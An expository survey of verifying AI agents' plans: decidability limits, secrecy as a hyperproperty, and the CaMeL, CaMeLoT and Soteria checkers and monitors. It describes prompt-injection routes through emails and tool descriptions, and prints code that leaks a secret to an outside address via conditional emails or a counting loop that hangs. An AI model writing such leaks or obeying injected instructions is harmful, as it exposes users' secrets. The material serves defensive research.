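The plan is in effect a finite-state machine, which reads its input one item at a time and can only be in one of a fixed number of states. This plan has two states, because `seen_urgent` is either true or false. If some long list of invoices leads to a payment, the plan must be in the same state at two points along the way, and removing the invoices between those points doesn't affect what follows. Repeating this leaves a list of at most two invoices that still leads to a payment. Each invoice is urgent or not and approved or not, which makes four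 kinds, so a checker has to try only 1 + 4 + 16 = 21 lists. Trying them would reveal that an urgent invoice followed by an unapproved one triggers a payment. matklad uses the same repetition of states to prove that such machines cannot count, but adds rounds of the cycle instead of removing them.

This argument does not apply to the plan that simulated a machine with one step per invoice, because its `state` can grow without limit. Unbounded loops are banned in both cases, but the plans differ in how much they can store and what arithmetic they can do. Bounded loops and unlimited numbers together are enough to bring undecidability back.

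### Ignoring the conditions

The approach that takes the least computation ignores the conditions and assumes that every branch is possible. The checker draws a graph with one point for each statement and an arrow from each statement to any that could come next. An `if` has two arrows leaving it, and a loop has an arrow back to its beginning. Starting from the first statement, the checker marks everything it can reach by following arrows. If it marks no call to `pay`, no run of the plan calls `pay`.

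The search visits each arrow at most once, so it takes a fraction of a second for any plan short enough for a person to read. It is sound, because every real run follows arrows in the graph. But it raises false alarms, because the graph also contains routes that no run can take. The plan with the contradictory fee conditions would fail this check, although it never pays. Some existing checkers for agents build on graphs of this kind. *Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026), for example, describes a larger system that includes a check of which steps in an agent's workflow are reachable.

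This procedure doesn't require a restricted language. A `while` loop in Python adds another arrow back to an earlier statement, and the search works whether or not the loop ever ends. It can therefore answer "might some route reach `pay`?" quickly and soundly, even for programs that may run forever. A restricted language mainly adds precision. With linear arithmetic and no loops, a checker can distinguish contradictory conditions from ones that can hold, so it can accept plans that the cruder search rejects. A checker for Python can also follow conditions, often well, but there will always be cases where it must approximate or return no answer.

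The search depends on knowing which tool each statement calls, which is difficult in Python. A Python program can join "p" and "ay" into a name and call whatever tool has that name, or take the name from an email. It can also contain `send_email = pay`, after which every line that appears to send an email makes a payment. A sound checker would have to assume that such a line might call any tool the plan can reach. If a language bans calls built at run time and doesn't let programs pass tools around like ordinary values, a reader can list a plan's possible calls from its text, whether or not the language allows unbounded loops.

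Often the useful question is whether a plan can pay without first testing something. In the repaired invoice plan, `pay` sits inside `if invoice.account in approved_accounts`. The checker can delete the arrow from that test to its "yes" branch and search the graph again. If the search can no longer reach `pay`, every run that pays must have passed the test. This also works in Python if `invoice` can't change between the test and the payment. The checker has to confirm that it can't, because Python lets other parts of a program alter a shared object. In a language where values never change after the plan creates them, the checker can skip this step.

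### Rules about one run and rules that compare runs

"This plan never calls `pay`" is a safety property in the technical sense, because any run that breaks it does so at a definite moment. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives other examples, including "the plan never writes to the network after reading a file" and access control, which requires every operation to match the rights of whoever requested it. Its example of a liveness property is guaranteed service, under which every request eventually gets a response. All of these are rules about single runs, so a complete record of one run shows whether that run kept the rule. A plan keeps the rule if all its runs do. *Hyperproperties* reports that Alpern and Schneider proved every rule of this type is a combination of a safety property and a liveness property.

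Safety properties reduce to the question this section began with. To check the rule about files and the network, we can add a variable that becomes true when the plan reads a file and, before each network write, a call to `alarm()` that runs only if the variable is true. We then ask whether any input makes the plan call `alarm`. If the language can express these additions, that question is decidable exactly when the question about `pay` is.

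Secrecy is different. The following plan obeys the rule "never email a value that came from `read_secret`":

```
if read_secret("payroll")[0] == "a":
    send_email("someone@elsewhere.example", "Hello")
```

Suppose a plan sends an email containing only a greeting if a password starts with "a", and sends nothing otherwise. The recipient can tell whether the password starts with "a" by whether the email arrives. This leak can't be detected from the record of a single run, only by comparing the run with what would have happened if the password had been different.

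Clarkson and Schneider call such rules hyperproperties. A single-run rule picks out which runs are acceptable, while a hyperproperty picks out which sets of runs are acceptable, taking all the runs of a plan together. One of their formulations of secrecy is

∀t, t′ ∈ T: t[0] =ₗ t′[0] ⇒ t ≈ₗ t′

where T is the set of all the plan's runs, t[0] is the first state of the run t, and the small l stands for an observer with low clearance. In words: if two runs look the same to an outsider at the start, they must go on looking the same. Only the secret may differ at the start, so the outsider can learn nothing about it. Secrecy isn't the only case. "The mean response time over all runs is under one second" is also a hyperproperty, because one slow run is acceptable if the others are fast enough.

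A checker can test the formula by placing two copies of the plan side by side, with the same ordinary inputs but separate secrets, and adding an `alarm` call that runs if an outsider would see the copies behave differently. Whether any input sets off the alarm is again decidable for plans with linear arithmetic and no loops, and undecidable for the richer languages. Clarkson and Schneider proved more generally that ordinary methods for safety properties extend to rules whose violations always show up in some fixed number of runs, but they had no complete method for other rules. *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties* (Finkbeiner, 2025) surveys the many specification languages and checking algorithms developed since.

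In the unrestricted case, a checker can fall back on an approximation similar to the graph search. It marks every value that depends on a secret and forbids visible actions inside any branch whose condition depends on a marked value. This rejects the "Hello" plan, but it also rejects some plans that leak nothing, such as one that sends the same greeting in both branches.

A monitor that watches an agent's tool calls as they happen sees only one run, so it can't judge secrecy directly and has to rely on a stricter single-run rule instead. If a company approves a loose plan and the model fills in the details later, a single-run rule that held for all runs of the loose plan still holds, but a secrecy rule needs checking again. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that outputs 0, 1 or a secret bit, choosing among the three arbitrarily. The possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the secret,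 so the system satisfies the rule "the possible outputs don't depend on the secret". If the system is narrowed so that it always outputs the secret bit, it breaks that rule, even though each of its runs was also a run of the original.

### What termination adds

Termination does give a checker two things, although each comes with conditions. The first concerns liveness properties, the rules with "eventually" in them. Suppose finance must eventually get an email after every payment, and the agent writes:

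```
pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
while not bank_confirms(invoice.number):
    wait(60)
send_email("finance", "Paid " + invoice.number)
```

Every route from the payment to the end of the plan passes through the email. But if the bank never confirms, the run stays in the loop forever and finance never gets the email. To approve this plan, a checker would have to prove that the loop ends, and no algorithm can do that for every loop. If a loop of at most sixty rounds replaces the `while`, every run reaches the end of the plan, so the checker only has to search the graph for a route from `pay` to the end that avoids `send_email`. If there isn't one, the rule holds.

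A step limit makes every run stop, but it can stop a run between the payment and the email. This counts against matklad's suggestion that a step limit does the same job as a terminating language. A time limit on a tool has the same effect if it kills the plan, but not if it returns a failure that the plan can handle. The advantage of a terminating language is still modest, since a promise that the email will be sent "eventually" is of little use to a finance team. A rule such as "finance gets an email within ten calls of a payment" is more useful, and it is a safety property.

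The second benefit concerns secrets. Clarkson and Schneider point out that the secrecy formula above, in the version they take from earlier work, compares two runs only as far as the shorter one goes. So it permits leaks through whether a program finishes. For years researchers thought this harmless, on the ground that finishing or hanging conveys one bit at most. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*, showed that the reasoning fails as soon as a program can produce output along the way. Here is their example in the terms of the office assistant, with a number as the secret:

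```
for i in range(1000000000):
    send_email("someone@elsewhere.example", i)
    if i == secret:
        while True:
            pass
```

A plan can leak a secret number by emailing 0, 1, 2 and so on until it reaches the secret, then hanging. The last number to arrive is the secret. The approximate check for secrecy passes this plan because the emails are outside the branch that depends on the secret, and the branch does nothing visible. Three established information-flow tools, Jif, FlowCaml and the SPARK Examiner, accepted programs of this form.

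To measure the leak, Askarov and colleagues had their program store each number in shared memory while a second process watched for the numbers to stop. On a 3 GHz machine they extracted a 32-bit secret in under six seconds, and they estimated that a credit card number would take about eighteen and a half days. They also proved that an attacker can do essentially no better than counting through the possibilities against a program that passes such a check, so a 128-bit encryption key is infeasible to extract. An agent that leaks by email would count much more slowly, but it would need at most 10,000 messages to leak a four-digit PIN.

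Nobody can write `while True` in a terminating language, so a secret can't leak through whether the plan hangs. But a crash, or a bounded loop that would take centuries, looks the same to the recipient as an infinite loop. Askarov and colleagues replaced the infinite loop with a function that called itself until the program ran out of memory, and the leak worked just as well. In a terminating language with division, an agent could replace the last three lines with `x = 1 / (i - secret)`, which crashes when `i` equals `secret`. A monitor that aborts the plan when a tool misbehaves could have the same effect if the misbehaviour depends on a secret.

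To close the channel completely, a language would have to ensure that neither failure nor running time depends on a secret. One known way is to forbid any loop whose condition involves a secret, which Askarov and colleagues call "draconian". *Reconciling progress-insensitive noninterference and declassification* describes the usual choice as strict rules for untrusted code and permissive rules for code that isn't written to exploit the gap. Bay and Askarov look for a middle course for systems that mix the two. A language model's plan fits neither category well, because it isn't normally written to leak passwords, but the model may have read an attacker's text before writing it.

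### Rights that change over time

So far the tools available to a plan have stayed the same, but some tools change what an agent may do by creating access tokens, sharing folders or adding users to groups. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman analysed this problem in *Protection in Operating Systems* (1976) and gave "safety" another technical meaning. In their model, a table records which rights each user or program holds over each object, and a fixed set of commands can alter the table. A system is safe for a particular right if a given user or program can never acquire that right to a given object.

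Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman proved, under assumptions they called "surprisingly weak", that no algorithm can decide in general whether a set of commands can ever add a dangerous right to the table of rights. Each command has no loops. It checks for certain rights and then makes a few changes. But the commands can run in any order, any number of times, while the table grows. The table can then serve as the memory of a simulated machine, set up so that the dangerous right appears only if the machine stops. According to Purdue University's lecture slides *The Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Model*, the question is undecidable even when commands can only add to the table.

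An agent may write a new plan every hour for years. Each plan is short and certain to finish, but the sequence of plans acts as an unbounded loop outside the language. For example, one plan shares a folder, another creates a token that can read the folder, and a third uses the token. A checker that examines each plan alone may find nothing wrong with any of them.

The question becomes decidable under some restrictions on how rights can change. Harrison and colleagues identified some of these cases, including systems in which each command makes only one change to the table. They placed that case in NP, the class of problems whose positive answers are easy to verify. Decades later, Tripunitara and Li's *The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited* showed that the proof depended on a false assumption and presented a correction. Also in 1976, Jones, Lipton and Snyder described a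 specific system whose security can be decided in time proportional to its size, as recounted in O'Reilly's textbook chapter *Foundational Results*. The question is simpler for the office assistant if none of its tools can grant rights or create accounts. Nothing it does then adds a right to the table, so the question reduces to which rights it holds at the start.

### Questions and languages compared

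The table assumes that plans call tools only by name, that numbers can be any size except where an input has a fixed list of values, and that every tool call returns an answer. A question counts as "decidable" only if it can be answered exactly, without false alarms.

| Question about a plan | Unbounded loops | Bounded loops | No loops, with multiplication | No loops, with finite values or linear arithmetic |
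|---|---|---|---|---|
| Which tools lie on some route, ignoring conditions? | Quick graph search | Quick graph search | Quick graph search | Quick graph search |
| Does it finish on every input? | Undecidable | Always yes | Always yes | Always yes |
| Does it call `pay` on one given input? | Undecidable | Decidable by running it | Decidable by running it | Decidable by running it |
| Does it call `pay` on any input? | Undecidable | Undecidable | Undecidable | Decidable, but NP-hard |
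| Does an email follow every payment? | Undecidable | Undecidable, but a graph search is sound | Undecidable, but a graph search is sound | Decidable, but slow in the worst case |
| Do two plans make the same calls on every input? | Undecidable | Undecidable, but a search finds any difference | Undecidable, but a search finds any difference | Decidable, but slow in the worst case |
| Can what an outsider sees depend on a secret? | Undecidable | Undecidable | Undecidable | Decidable, but slow in the worst case |

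## What can plan checkers prove before a plan runs?

Several research groups have built checkers for agents' plans. Many exact questions about plans are undecidable or slow to answer, so every checker simplifies somewhere. A checker may ignore a plan's conditions, ban loops, or check some rules only while the plan is running.

Dantas and colleagues group the 38 studies they survey by when the checking happens. A check before the run can reject a plan before anything irreversible happens, but it needs the complete plan. Checking each action as it comes up also works for agents that choose as they go, but it cannot cover steps the agent hasn't chosen yet. Fifteen of the studies check before the run and eight check during it.

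### Generate, verify, then execute

Writing the plan first protects against the malicious email in Meijer's example, because the assistant has settled its steps before it opens the inbox. It doesn't help if the attacker's text reaches the model while the model is still writing the plan, which Meijer says can happen in two ways. The written description that tells the agent what the mail tool does might include an instruction to send summaries of all emails to an outside address, or a malicious user might ask for such a step. The model may then write a well-formed plan that fetches the mail, summarises it and sends the summary to the attacker.

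Meijer proposes that a checker test each plan, before it runs, against rules the company has already written. He calls this "generate, verify, then execute". In his example, a plan breaks the rule if data can travel from a source, where sensitive data enters the plan, to a sink, where the data could do harm. The source is the result of `fetch_email`, and the sink is the body of `send_email` when the recipient's address is outside the company's domain. Meijer suggests that existing tools for finding security flaws in code, such as CodeQL and Semgrep, could search for such routes.

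The same kind of rule, with `read_secret` as the source, stops the office assistant's one-line plan to email the payroll password to an outsider. A checker can determine from the plan's text that the password goes into the email's body and the address is outside the company. If the plan took the address from an invoice, a sound checker would have to reject it too. But the plan that emails "Hello" only for some passwords would pass, because the email contains no part of the password.

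Meijer compares this with Java and .NET, which verify a program's compiled code before running it. He also wants the agent to supply a formal proof that its plan is safe. Finding a proof may be hard, but checking one is easy, and a checker will reject a bad proof whoever wrote it, so nobody has to trust the model. Meijer accepts that some checks must happen while the plan runs. Java and .NET, for instance, check every array index as the program uses it, because their verifiers do not work out the range of the indexes. He also notes that nobody had formally measured how writing structured plans affects an agent's success. More recent work on checkers provides some measurements.

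### CaMeL checks each value's origin during the run

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind researchers published in 2025, enforces rules while the plan runs. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes CaMeL's design and proposes an extension. CaMeL uses two language models. The privileged model reads the user's request and writes a plan in restricted Python, which excludes constructs such as arbitrary `while` loops. The quarantined model reads untrusted text, such as emails and web pages. It has no tools and only extracts values in a fixed format, such as an email address. An ordinary software interpreter runs the plan, calls the tools and stores the results in variables.

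A malicious email can't add steps to such a plan, but it can still change a value, such as the account number passed to `pay`. CaMeL's interpreter therefore labels each value with its sources and with the people who may read it. Before each tool call, it runs a policy, a short Python function that checks the tool, the arguments and their labels, then allows or denies the call. One policy in the banking tests allows a password change only if the new password came from a trusted source, such as the user.

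A policy that payment details must come from the user would stop the three-line office plan at its second line. No harm is done, because the plan has only read some invoices by then. A longer plan may do much more before a policy stops it. Nikolaou and colleagues describe an agent that investigates a security alert and then disconnects the affected computer from the network, a step that requires approval. If the plan has no approval step, CaMeL will detect the omission only after the whole investigation has run. CaMeL also has no natural way to express a rule such as "close every ticket you open", because each policy checks only the current call.

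Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark whose 97 ordinary user tasks cover workplace chat, banking, travel and office work. With Claude Haiku 4.5 as the model and no attacks, CaMeL completed 49 tasks and blocked 26, all of them legitimate requests. In the other 22, the plan ran but didn't do what the user wanted. Some of the blocked plans may have been faulty, but a strict rule about where data comes from also stops reasonable plans. For example, the employee who asked the assistant to pay the oldest invoice wanted it to use an account number from the invoice.

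### CaMeLoT moves the check before the run

CaMeLoT keeps CaMeL's interpreter and policies and adds a check between writing the plan and running it. The office plan shows how it works:

```
invoice = read_invoices()[0]
pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
send_email("finance", "Paid " + invoice.number)
```

CaMeLoT begins by turning the plan into a finite-state machine, which resembles the graph of statements and arrows in the last section. This plan becomes a single line of five states:

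start → `read_invoices` → `pay` → `send_email` → done

Next come the provenance labels. There are four, in order of increasing suspicion:

trusted < user < untrusted < quarantined model

A constant written in the plan is trusted. Parameters of the user's query get the label "user", results from outside tools are untrusted, and anything the quarantined model produces gets the least trusted label. A value computed from several others takes the least trusted of their labels. In the office plan, `invoice` is untrusted, and so are the account, amount and invoice number. The word "finance" is trusted, but the email's text is untrusted because it contains the invoice number. CaMeLoT attaches these facts to the states, so the state for `pay` records that the account and amount are both tainted, meaning they come from one of the two least trusted origins. The state also records which tools the plan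 has already called.

The rules are formulas in computation tree logic, a language for statements about the possible futures of a system. **AG** means "in every state, on every path", and **AF** means "eventually, on every path". A payment rule that Nikolaou and colleagues give looks like this with the office tool's name:

**AG**(call_pay ⇒ ¬(account_tainted ∨ amount_tainted))

In words: whenever the plan calls `pay`, neither the account nor the amount is tainted.

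CaMeLoT then passes the machine and the rule to nuXmv, a model checker, which tests a formula against every possible run of a finite machine. nuXmv finds both call_pay and account_tainted in the `pay` state, so the rule is false. It returns a counterexample, a run that breaks the rule, in which the plan starts, reads the invoices and pays a tainted account. A person could check these five states by eye, but the same procedure covers every combination of branches in a longer plan.

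CaMeLoT turns the counterexample into a plain-language message that includes the broken rule and the path that broke it, and the privileged model rewrites the plan. This cycle repeats, before any tool runs, until a plan passes or the attempt limit is reached.

Adding `if invoice.account in approved_accounts` would not make the plan pass, because CaMeLoT leaves conditions out of its machine. The machine would still have a path to `pay` with a tainted account, so the rule would still be false. To pass, the plan would have to get the account from somewhere else, such as the company's own supplier records, if the company has configured CaMeLoT to trust them.

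Conversely, `pay("account-7731", 9500)` passes this rule, because the account and the amount are constants and CaMeLoT labels constants as trusted. This makes sense if the privileged model has seen only trustworthy text, since the number should then have come from the user. The label is wrong if the model invented the number or took it from a tool description of the kind Meijer worries about. The proof covers only how values move through the plan once the model has written it.

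Knowing that a plan terminates helps when checking loops. CaMeLoT's example rules include **AF**(done), which requires every run to end. In the machine, a loop is a choice, after each round, between repeating and leaving, so one possible run repeats forever. The rule would therefore be false of the machine even though every loop in the plan is bounded. Engineers can configure a model checker to ignore endless runs, which is justified here because the plan language has no endless loops. Ordinary Python does allow them, so the same setting could hide a real fault there.

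### What the tests of CaMeLoT measured

Nikolaou and colleagues rewrote CaMeL's policies for AgentDojo as temporal rules to see how many a checker could test before a run. The rules fully covered 22 of the 28 security policies, including all 11 for banking and travel but only three of the seven for workplace chat. The other six depend on facts that aren't available until the plan runs. For the confidentiality policies, which govern who may read what, the checker matched CaMeL in 16 of 28 cases, and only because the data in those cases was public. A plan's text doesn't show who will have access to a shared file when the agent sends it.

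On the 97 tasks, CaMeLoT and CaMeL made the same decision about 59 plans, and another 22 failed under both. CaMeLoT passed nine plans that CaMeL blocked, mostly because of facts that emerged during the run. These nine passes aren't dangerous in practice, since CaMeL's policies still apply after CaMeLoT has passed a plan. CaMeLoT also blocked seven plans that CaMeL completed. Six of these were office tasks, where a calendar entry may be trustworthy if the user wrote it and untrustworthy if somebody else did. CaMeLoT has to treat such entries as untrustworthy, so these were probably false alarms. Nikolaou and colleagues argue that a false alarm often adds just one round of planning, which wastes less than abandoning a plan halfway.

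Another experiment used rules that CaMeL can't easily express. The researchers wrote a safe plan for handling a security alert, with steps to confirm which computer was affected, open a ticket, request approval, disconnect the computer and resolve the incident. They wrote seven rules about such plans and made seven unsafe versions of the plan by hand, each breaking one rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven. A simplified CaMeL caught one, in which the plan blocked a network address that the quarantined model had supplied.

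This comparison gives little evidence of how the systems would compare in use. Nikolaou and colleagues chose the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can check and expected it to miss most of the plans. Each unsafe plan broke a rule that CaMeLoT already had, so catching all seven shows that the software works as designed, but not how many unsafe plans it would catch in a real company. In four further tests, Claude Haiku 4.5 wrote the unsafe plans itself, after requests such as one to skip the approval because time was short, and CaMeLoT caught those too.

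Some of the seven rules are also weaker or stronger than their descriptions. "Human approval before strong action" is written as a formula that holds once the plan has called `request_ir_approval`, whatever the answer. The safe plan requests approval and disconnects the computer on the next line without checking the reply. Unless the tool waits until somebody agrees, the rule guarantees only that the plan requested approval. Another rule requires every run to disconnect the computer, so it would reject a sensible plan that disconnects it only if the alert turns out to be real.

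CaMeLoT can also derive rules from the user's request, to catch plans that obey every company rule but don't do the task. A language model fills in one of ten templates, such as "every run eventually calls this tool" or "this tool only after that one", and ordinary code converts the result into a formula. The filled-in templates listed exactly the right state-changing tools for 85 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks. In three of the other 12, the model had correctly treated an action as conditional, and in the remaining nine, the checker would have tested the plan against the wrong request.

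### Soteria keeps the conditions

Soteria, by He and colleagues, would accept the office plan that tests the account before paying, because it doesn't discard conditions. It represents a plan as a guarded transition system, which is a graph of states joined by transitions. A transition makes at most one tool call and may have a guard, a condition that has to be true before the plan can take it. The repaired office plan would look like this:

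```
READ  -> CHECK   call read_invoices
CHECK -> PAY     if the account is approved
CHECK -> STOP    otherwise
PAY   -> TELL    call pay
TELL  -> DONE    call send_email
```

For each state, Soteria works out a formula Σ containing everything that must be true whenever the plan is there. Moving along a transition adds its guard and whatever the tool's contract guarantees. If several transitions lead to the same state, Soteria joins their formulas with "or". Suppose the contract of `read_invoices` guarantees that every amount is positive. Then the formula for PAY is

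invoice.amount > 0 ∧ invoice.account ∈ approved_accounts

Soteria passes three kinds of question to Dafny, an automatic program verifier.

A plan checker can prove that every call meets its tool's contract. If P is what the tool requires and g is the guard, Dafny has to prove Σ ∧ g ⇒ P. If `pay` requires a positive amount and an approved account, the formula for PAY implies both. Without the test in CHECK, Dafny could not prove that the account is approved.

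Dafny also checks progress, meaning that the plan can't get stuck. Every state before the end must be reachable, and wherever the plan branches, at least one guard must be true:

Σ ⇒ g₁ ∨ g₂ ∨ … ∨ gₙ

A plan with one branch for invoices under 500 and another for invoices over 500 would fail the check, because neither branch covers an invoice for exactly 500. The plan in the last section whose conditions on the fee contradict each other would also fail. That plan is harmless, but a branch that can never run is usually a mistake.

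The remaining question is whether every run obeys the company's policies. For this, Soteria adds bookkeeping that exists only in the proof: a step counter, a log of calls with their arguments and results, and a record of which tools' results fed into each value. One airline rule forbids cancelling a booking before checking that the customer has not already taken any of its flights:

∀c : cancel. ∃c′ : check_unflown. c′ ≺ c ∧ c′.booking = c.booking ∧ c′.result = true

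The symbol ≺ means "happened before". The rule requires that every cancellation come after a check on the same booking that came back clear. This is stricter than CaMeLoT's approval rule, which records only that some request took place. A Soteria rule can require that the answer was yes and that it concerned the right booking.

If a proof fails, the planning model gets an error message and tries again, up to eight times. Dafny may also run out of time on a rule, as expected from the limits on decidability, and He and colleagues allow it ten seconds per state. Soteria then continues with the best partly verified plan and warns the model about the unproved rules. A library of sub-plans makes planning easier. Each sub-plan is a standard procedure that Soteria has already verified, and a plan can call it like a tool. With the library, 65 of 68 airline plans passed within the eight attempts, compared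 with 38 of 60 without it.

Besides true tool contracts, these proofs need a plan whose graph has no cycles, although a single step can apply an action to each item in a list. If a step asks a language model for a judgement, the proof assumes that the answer meets a stated condition, which Soteria tests when the answer arrives. Wang and colleagues make a stronger assumption in their checker for agent workflows, that a model can produce a step's intended result if it starts with everything the step requires. Their proofs therefore show that the steps fit together, for example that no step uses information that no earlier step supplies. In their tests, workflows that passed did better than those that failed by an average of 11.94%. This is evidence that checking finds badly designed workflows, but it does not show that checking prevents harm.

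### A verified plan, and the model that carries it out

He and colleagues tested Soteria's parts on 50 airline customer-service tasks, adding one part at a time and counting violations of the airline's rules. The top row comes from their main comparison, in which the agent had the policy only in its instructions.

| Configuration | Violations, GPT-5.4-mini | Violations, Gemini 3 Flash |
|---|---|---|
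| Policy in the instructions, no plan | 29 | 25 |
| Plan without verification | 13 | 27 |
| Verification added | 10 | 24 |
| Sub-plans added | 12 | 22 |
| Runtime monitor added | 0 | 0 |

Verifying the plan removed three violations for each model, which could be chance. When GPT-5.4-mini ran the same tasks five times without a plan, the number of violations had a standard deviation of about four. Having a plan at all helped GPT-5.4-mini much more than verifying it did, but seems not to have helped Gemini 3 Flash.

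The verified plans had so little effect because the executor, the model that carries out a plan, doesn't have to follow it. By default, Soteria shows the executor the plan as a flowchart that shrinks as results arrive, but the executor may still call any tool. The violations come from the executor's actions, which the proof doesn't cover. Plans that failed verification can explain few of the violations. With sub-plans but no monitor, GPT-5.4-mini broke a rule in 10 of the 50 tasks, although only three of 68 plans had failed verification in the comparison of sub-plans.

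The runtime monitor adds each call that the executor proposes to the log of the run so far, checks the rules, and blocks the call if it would break one. This reduced violations to zero for both models. In the main comparison, on 207 tasks from three benchmarks and with four models, Soteria had no violations, and no rival method kept the rules in more than 93% of tasks. The zeros are largely guaranteed, because the monitor enforces the same rules that the researchers used for scoring. The researchers also corrected and added some rules while auditing the results. The experiment is more convincing as evidence that an agent can work under such a monitor and still complete tasks, sometimes more of them than before.

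The ablation doesn't test the monitor without a verified plan, so it can't show how much verification adds once a monitor is running. Verification probably adds something, because a monitor can block a call but can't make an agent do something it has left out. For example, one benchmark requires the agent to confirm the contents of every file it writes by reading the file back. A monitor can detect a missing read only when the task ends, whereas a checker can reject the plan before it runs. Verification also costs more, because Soteria writes a new plan at each turn of a conversation. An airline task with GPT-5.4-mini cost 12.5 cents, against 3.1 cents for the agent without a plan.

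CaMeL avoids the problem of an executor that departs from the plan, because its interpreter runs the plan itself and no model chooses tool calls during the run. Whatever a checker proves about the plan is therefore also true of the run, provided that the interpreter is correct and the tools have the right labels. Soteria has a similar strict mode, in which only fully verified plans can run and the executor may make only the calls that the plan allows at that point. This mode can refuse harmless calls that the user wanted. In an example from He and colleagues, a user asks the agent to cancel one reservation and look up another. If the plan covers only the cancellation, strict mode refuses the lookup.

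### How many rules need a plan checker

The checkers above can test only rules that somebody has written precisely. *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (Hong, She and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 80 benchmarks for agent security and safety. Of these, 49 state no requirements, and 19 state only goals, such as refusing "anything unsafe", without explaining what counts as unsafe. Seven contain requirements precise enough to verify.

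They then looked more closely at two of these seven. τ²-Bench covers airline customer service, and CAR-bench covers an in-car voice assistant. To include a high-stakes field, they added MedAgentBench, which tests assistants that work with medical records. That benchmark had no safety policy, so they had language models write one, partly from a systematic analysis of hazards.

The researchers sorted the requirements by hand. They set aside sentences that only gave information and requirements that no behaviour of the agent could fulfil. For each of the rest, they asked whether ordinary program code could enforce it by at least one of six methods:

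- validation, in which code tests a call's arguments before the call goes through
- schema constraints, which reject output in the wrong format
- temporal logic, which restricts the order of calls
- information-flow control, which limits where data can go
- confirmation by the user, which fixed code requests instead of leaving it to the model
- response templates, which replace the model's wording with a prepared text

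Code could enforce 42 of 51 requirements for the airline, 17 of 18 for the car and 34 of 57 for the medical assistant, or 74% overall. The researchers wrote the code for most of these, leaving out ten medical requirements that needed specialist knowledge, such as the right dosage units for each drug.

Most of the requirements that code could not enforce concern the agent's manner (such as staying neutral), forbid it to make things up, prescribe a procedure (such as collecting a customer's details before asking about the trip), or need common sense. For example, the airline's agent may not offer compensation unless the customer explicitly asks for it, and somebody has to judge what counts as asking. A company can sometimes replace such a requirement with a cruder one that code can enforce. Hong and colleagues suggest blocking the compensation tools until the customer replies with exactly the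 word "compensation". Code could check this easily, but customers would find it irritating.

Their finding that most weakens the case for plan checkers is that 88 of the 93 enforceable requirements needed only simple methods, mainly validation. The other five, all in the medical policy, needed temporal logic or information-flow control. A tool can validate its own arguments whether or not the agent has written a plan, and whatever language the plan is in. For example, He and colleagues express the airline's rule about flights already taken as a rule about the order of calls, and prove that plans obey it. Hong and colleagues would instead have the cancellation tool look up the flights and refuse any cancellation that breaks the rule, so that no plan can break it. Replacing `pay` with `pay_invoice` has the same effect for the office assistant.

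Agents need some such enforcement. Without it, the GPT-5 agent broke at least one enforceable rule in 20% of airline tasks and the older GPT-4o agent did so in 52%, although both had the whole policy in their instructions. Adding the enforcement code did not reduce the number of tasks completed. When a tool refused a call and gave the reason, the agent could often find an acceptable alternative.

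The count of five probably understates the need for plan checkers. It comes from three policies, one of them written by language models, and the tests mostly cover user requests. Provenance rules matter most when an attacker hides instructions in documents that the agent reads. A tool can't enforce such rules by looking at its arguments, because an attacker's account number looks like any other. The system has to track where the number came from, either by analysing the plan before it runs or by following the data during the run.

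### Five kinds of rule

Limits on quantities are harder to prove than they look. CaMeLoT's machine can't count the rounds of a loop, because it replaces the loop with a choice to continue or leave. Soteria can count calls in its log, and one of its airline rules allows at most three gift cards per booking. But if a plan pays every invoice on a list, the number of payments depends on the list's length. A checker can prove "at most forty payments" only if the contract of `read_invoices` caps the list at forty or the plan takes no more than the first forty. To prove a limit on the total paid, it also needs a cap on each invoice.

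The table assumes a restricted language in which plans call tools only by name and every loop is bounded.

| Kind of rule | Example | What a checker needs besides the language | What remains for the run |
|---|---|---|---|
| Allowed tools | The plan never calls `drop_table` | A true account of what each tool does, so that no other tool can also delete tables | Blocking other calls, if a model carries out the plan |
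| Argument provenance | The account in `pay` never comes from an email | Labels for the tools that return outside text, and a planning model that has read only trusted text | Origins that vary from item to item, such as who wrote a calendar entry |
| Order | An approval comes before every payment | A record of what the approval tool answered and which payment the answer covers | Whether the approver said yes |
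| Required follow-up | An email to finance follows every payment | Time limits on tools, a way for the plan to handle failures, and an interpreter or executor that follows the plan to its end | Whether the email arrived |
| Limits | The plan pays out at most 5,000 in total | Caps on the length of lists and on each amount, from tool contracts or from tests in the plan | The actual total, where no such cap exists |

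## Why can a plan pass every check and still be wrong?

The checkers in the last section compare a plan with written rules and assume that tools behave as described. If that assumption holds, a plan that passes obeys the rules, but it can still be wrong. The rule that would have stopped it may be missing or badly written. A tool may do something that its contract leaves out. An important fact may turn up only during the run, or the user may have wanted something they never mentioned.

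### A rule nobody wrote

Meijer describes a tool, `delete_file`, that accepts a pattern as well as a file name. The pattern `*.txt` matches every file whose name ends in ".txt". A user asks the agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The agent could call the tool twice, but it may prefer a shorter plan:

```
delete_file("*.txt")
```

In Meijer's example, the plan describes one step as deleting `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, but if the folder also holds `notes.txt`, the step deletes that too.

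To check the plan, a verifier needs the tool's contract and a postcondition, a statement of what must be true when the plan ends. Write F for the set of files before the run and F′ for the set afterwards. In Meijer's first version, the contract promises that every matching file disappears:

∀f: f ∈ glob(pattern) ⇒ f ∉ F′

Here glob(pattern) is the set of names that match the pattern. The postcondition of the plan is

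foo.txt ∉ F′ ∧ bar.txt ∉ F′

Both names match `*.txt`, so the contract guarantees that both files disappear, and the proof succeeds. The proof does not depend on what happens to `notes.txt`. Meijer concludes that the model "bears no blame", because it found the simplest plan that satisfies the postcondition.

The postcondition lacks a frame condition, which states that everything else stays as it was:

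∀f: f ∉ {foo.txt, bar.txt} ⇒ (f ∈ F′ ⇔ f ∈ F)

With this added, the short plan fails verification. The proof must hold for every folder the plan might run in, including one that contains `notes.txt`. In that folder `notes.txt` belongs to F, but its name matches the pattern, so the contract puts it outside F′, which violates the frame condition. The verifier rejects the plan even if the real folder holds only the two unwanted files, so the rejection is sometimes a false alarm.

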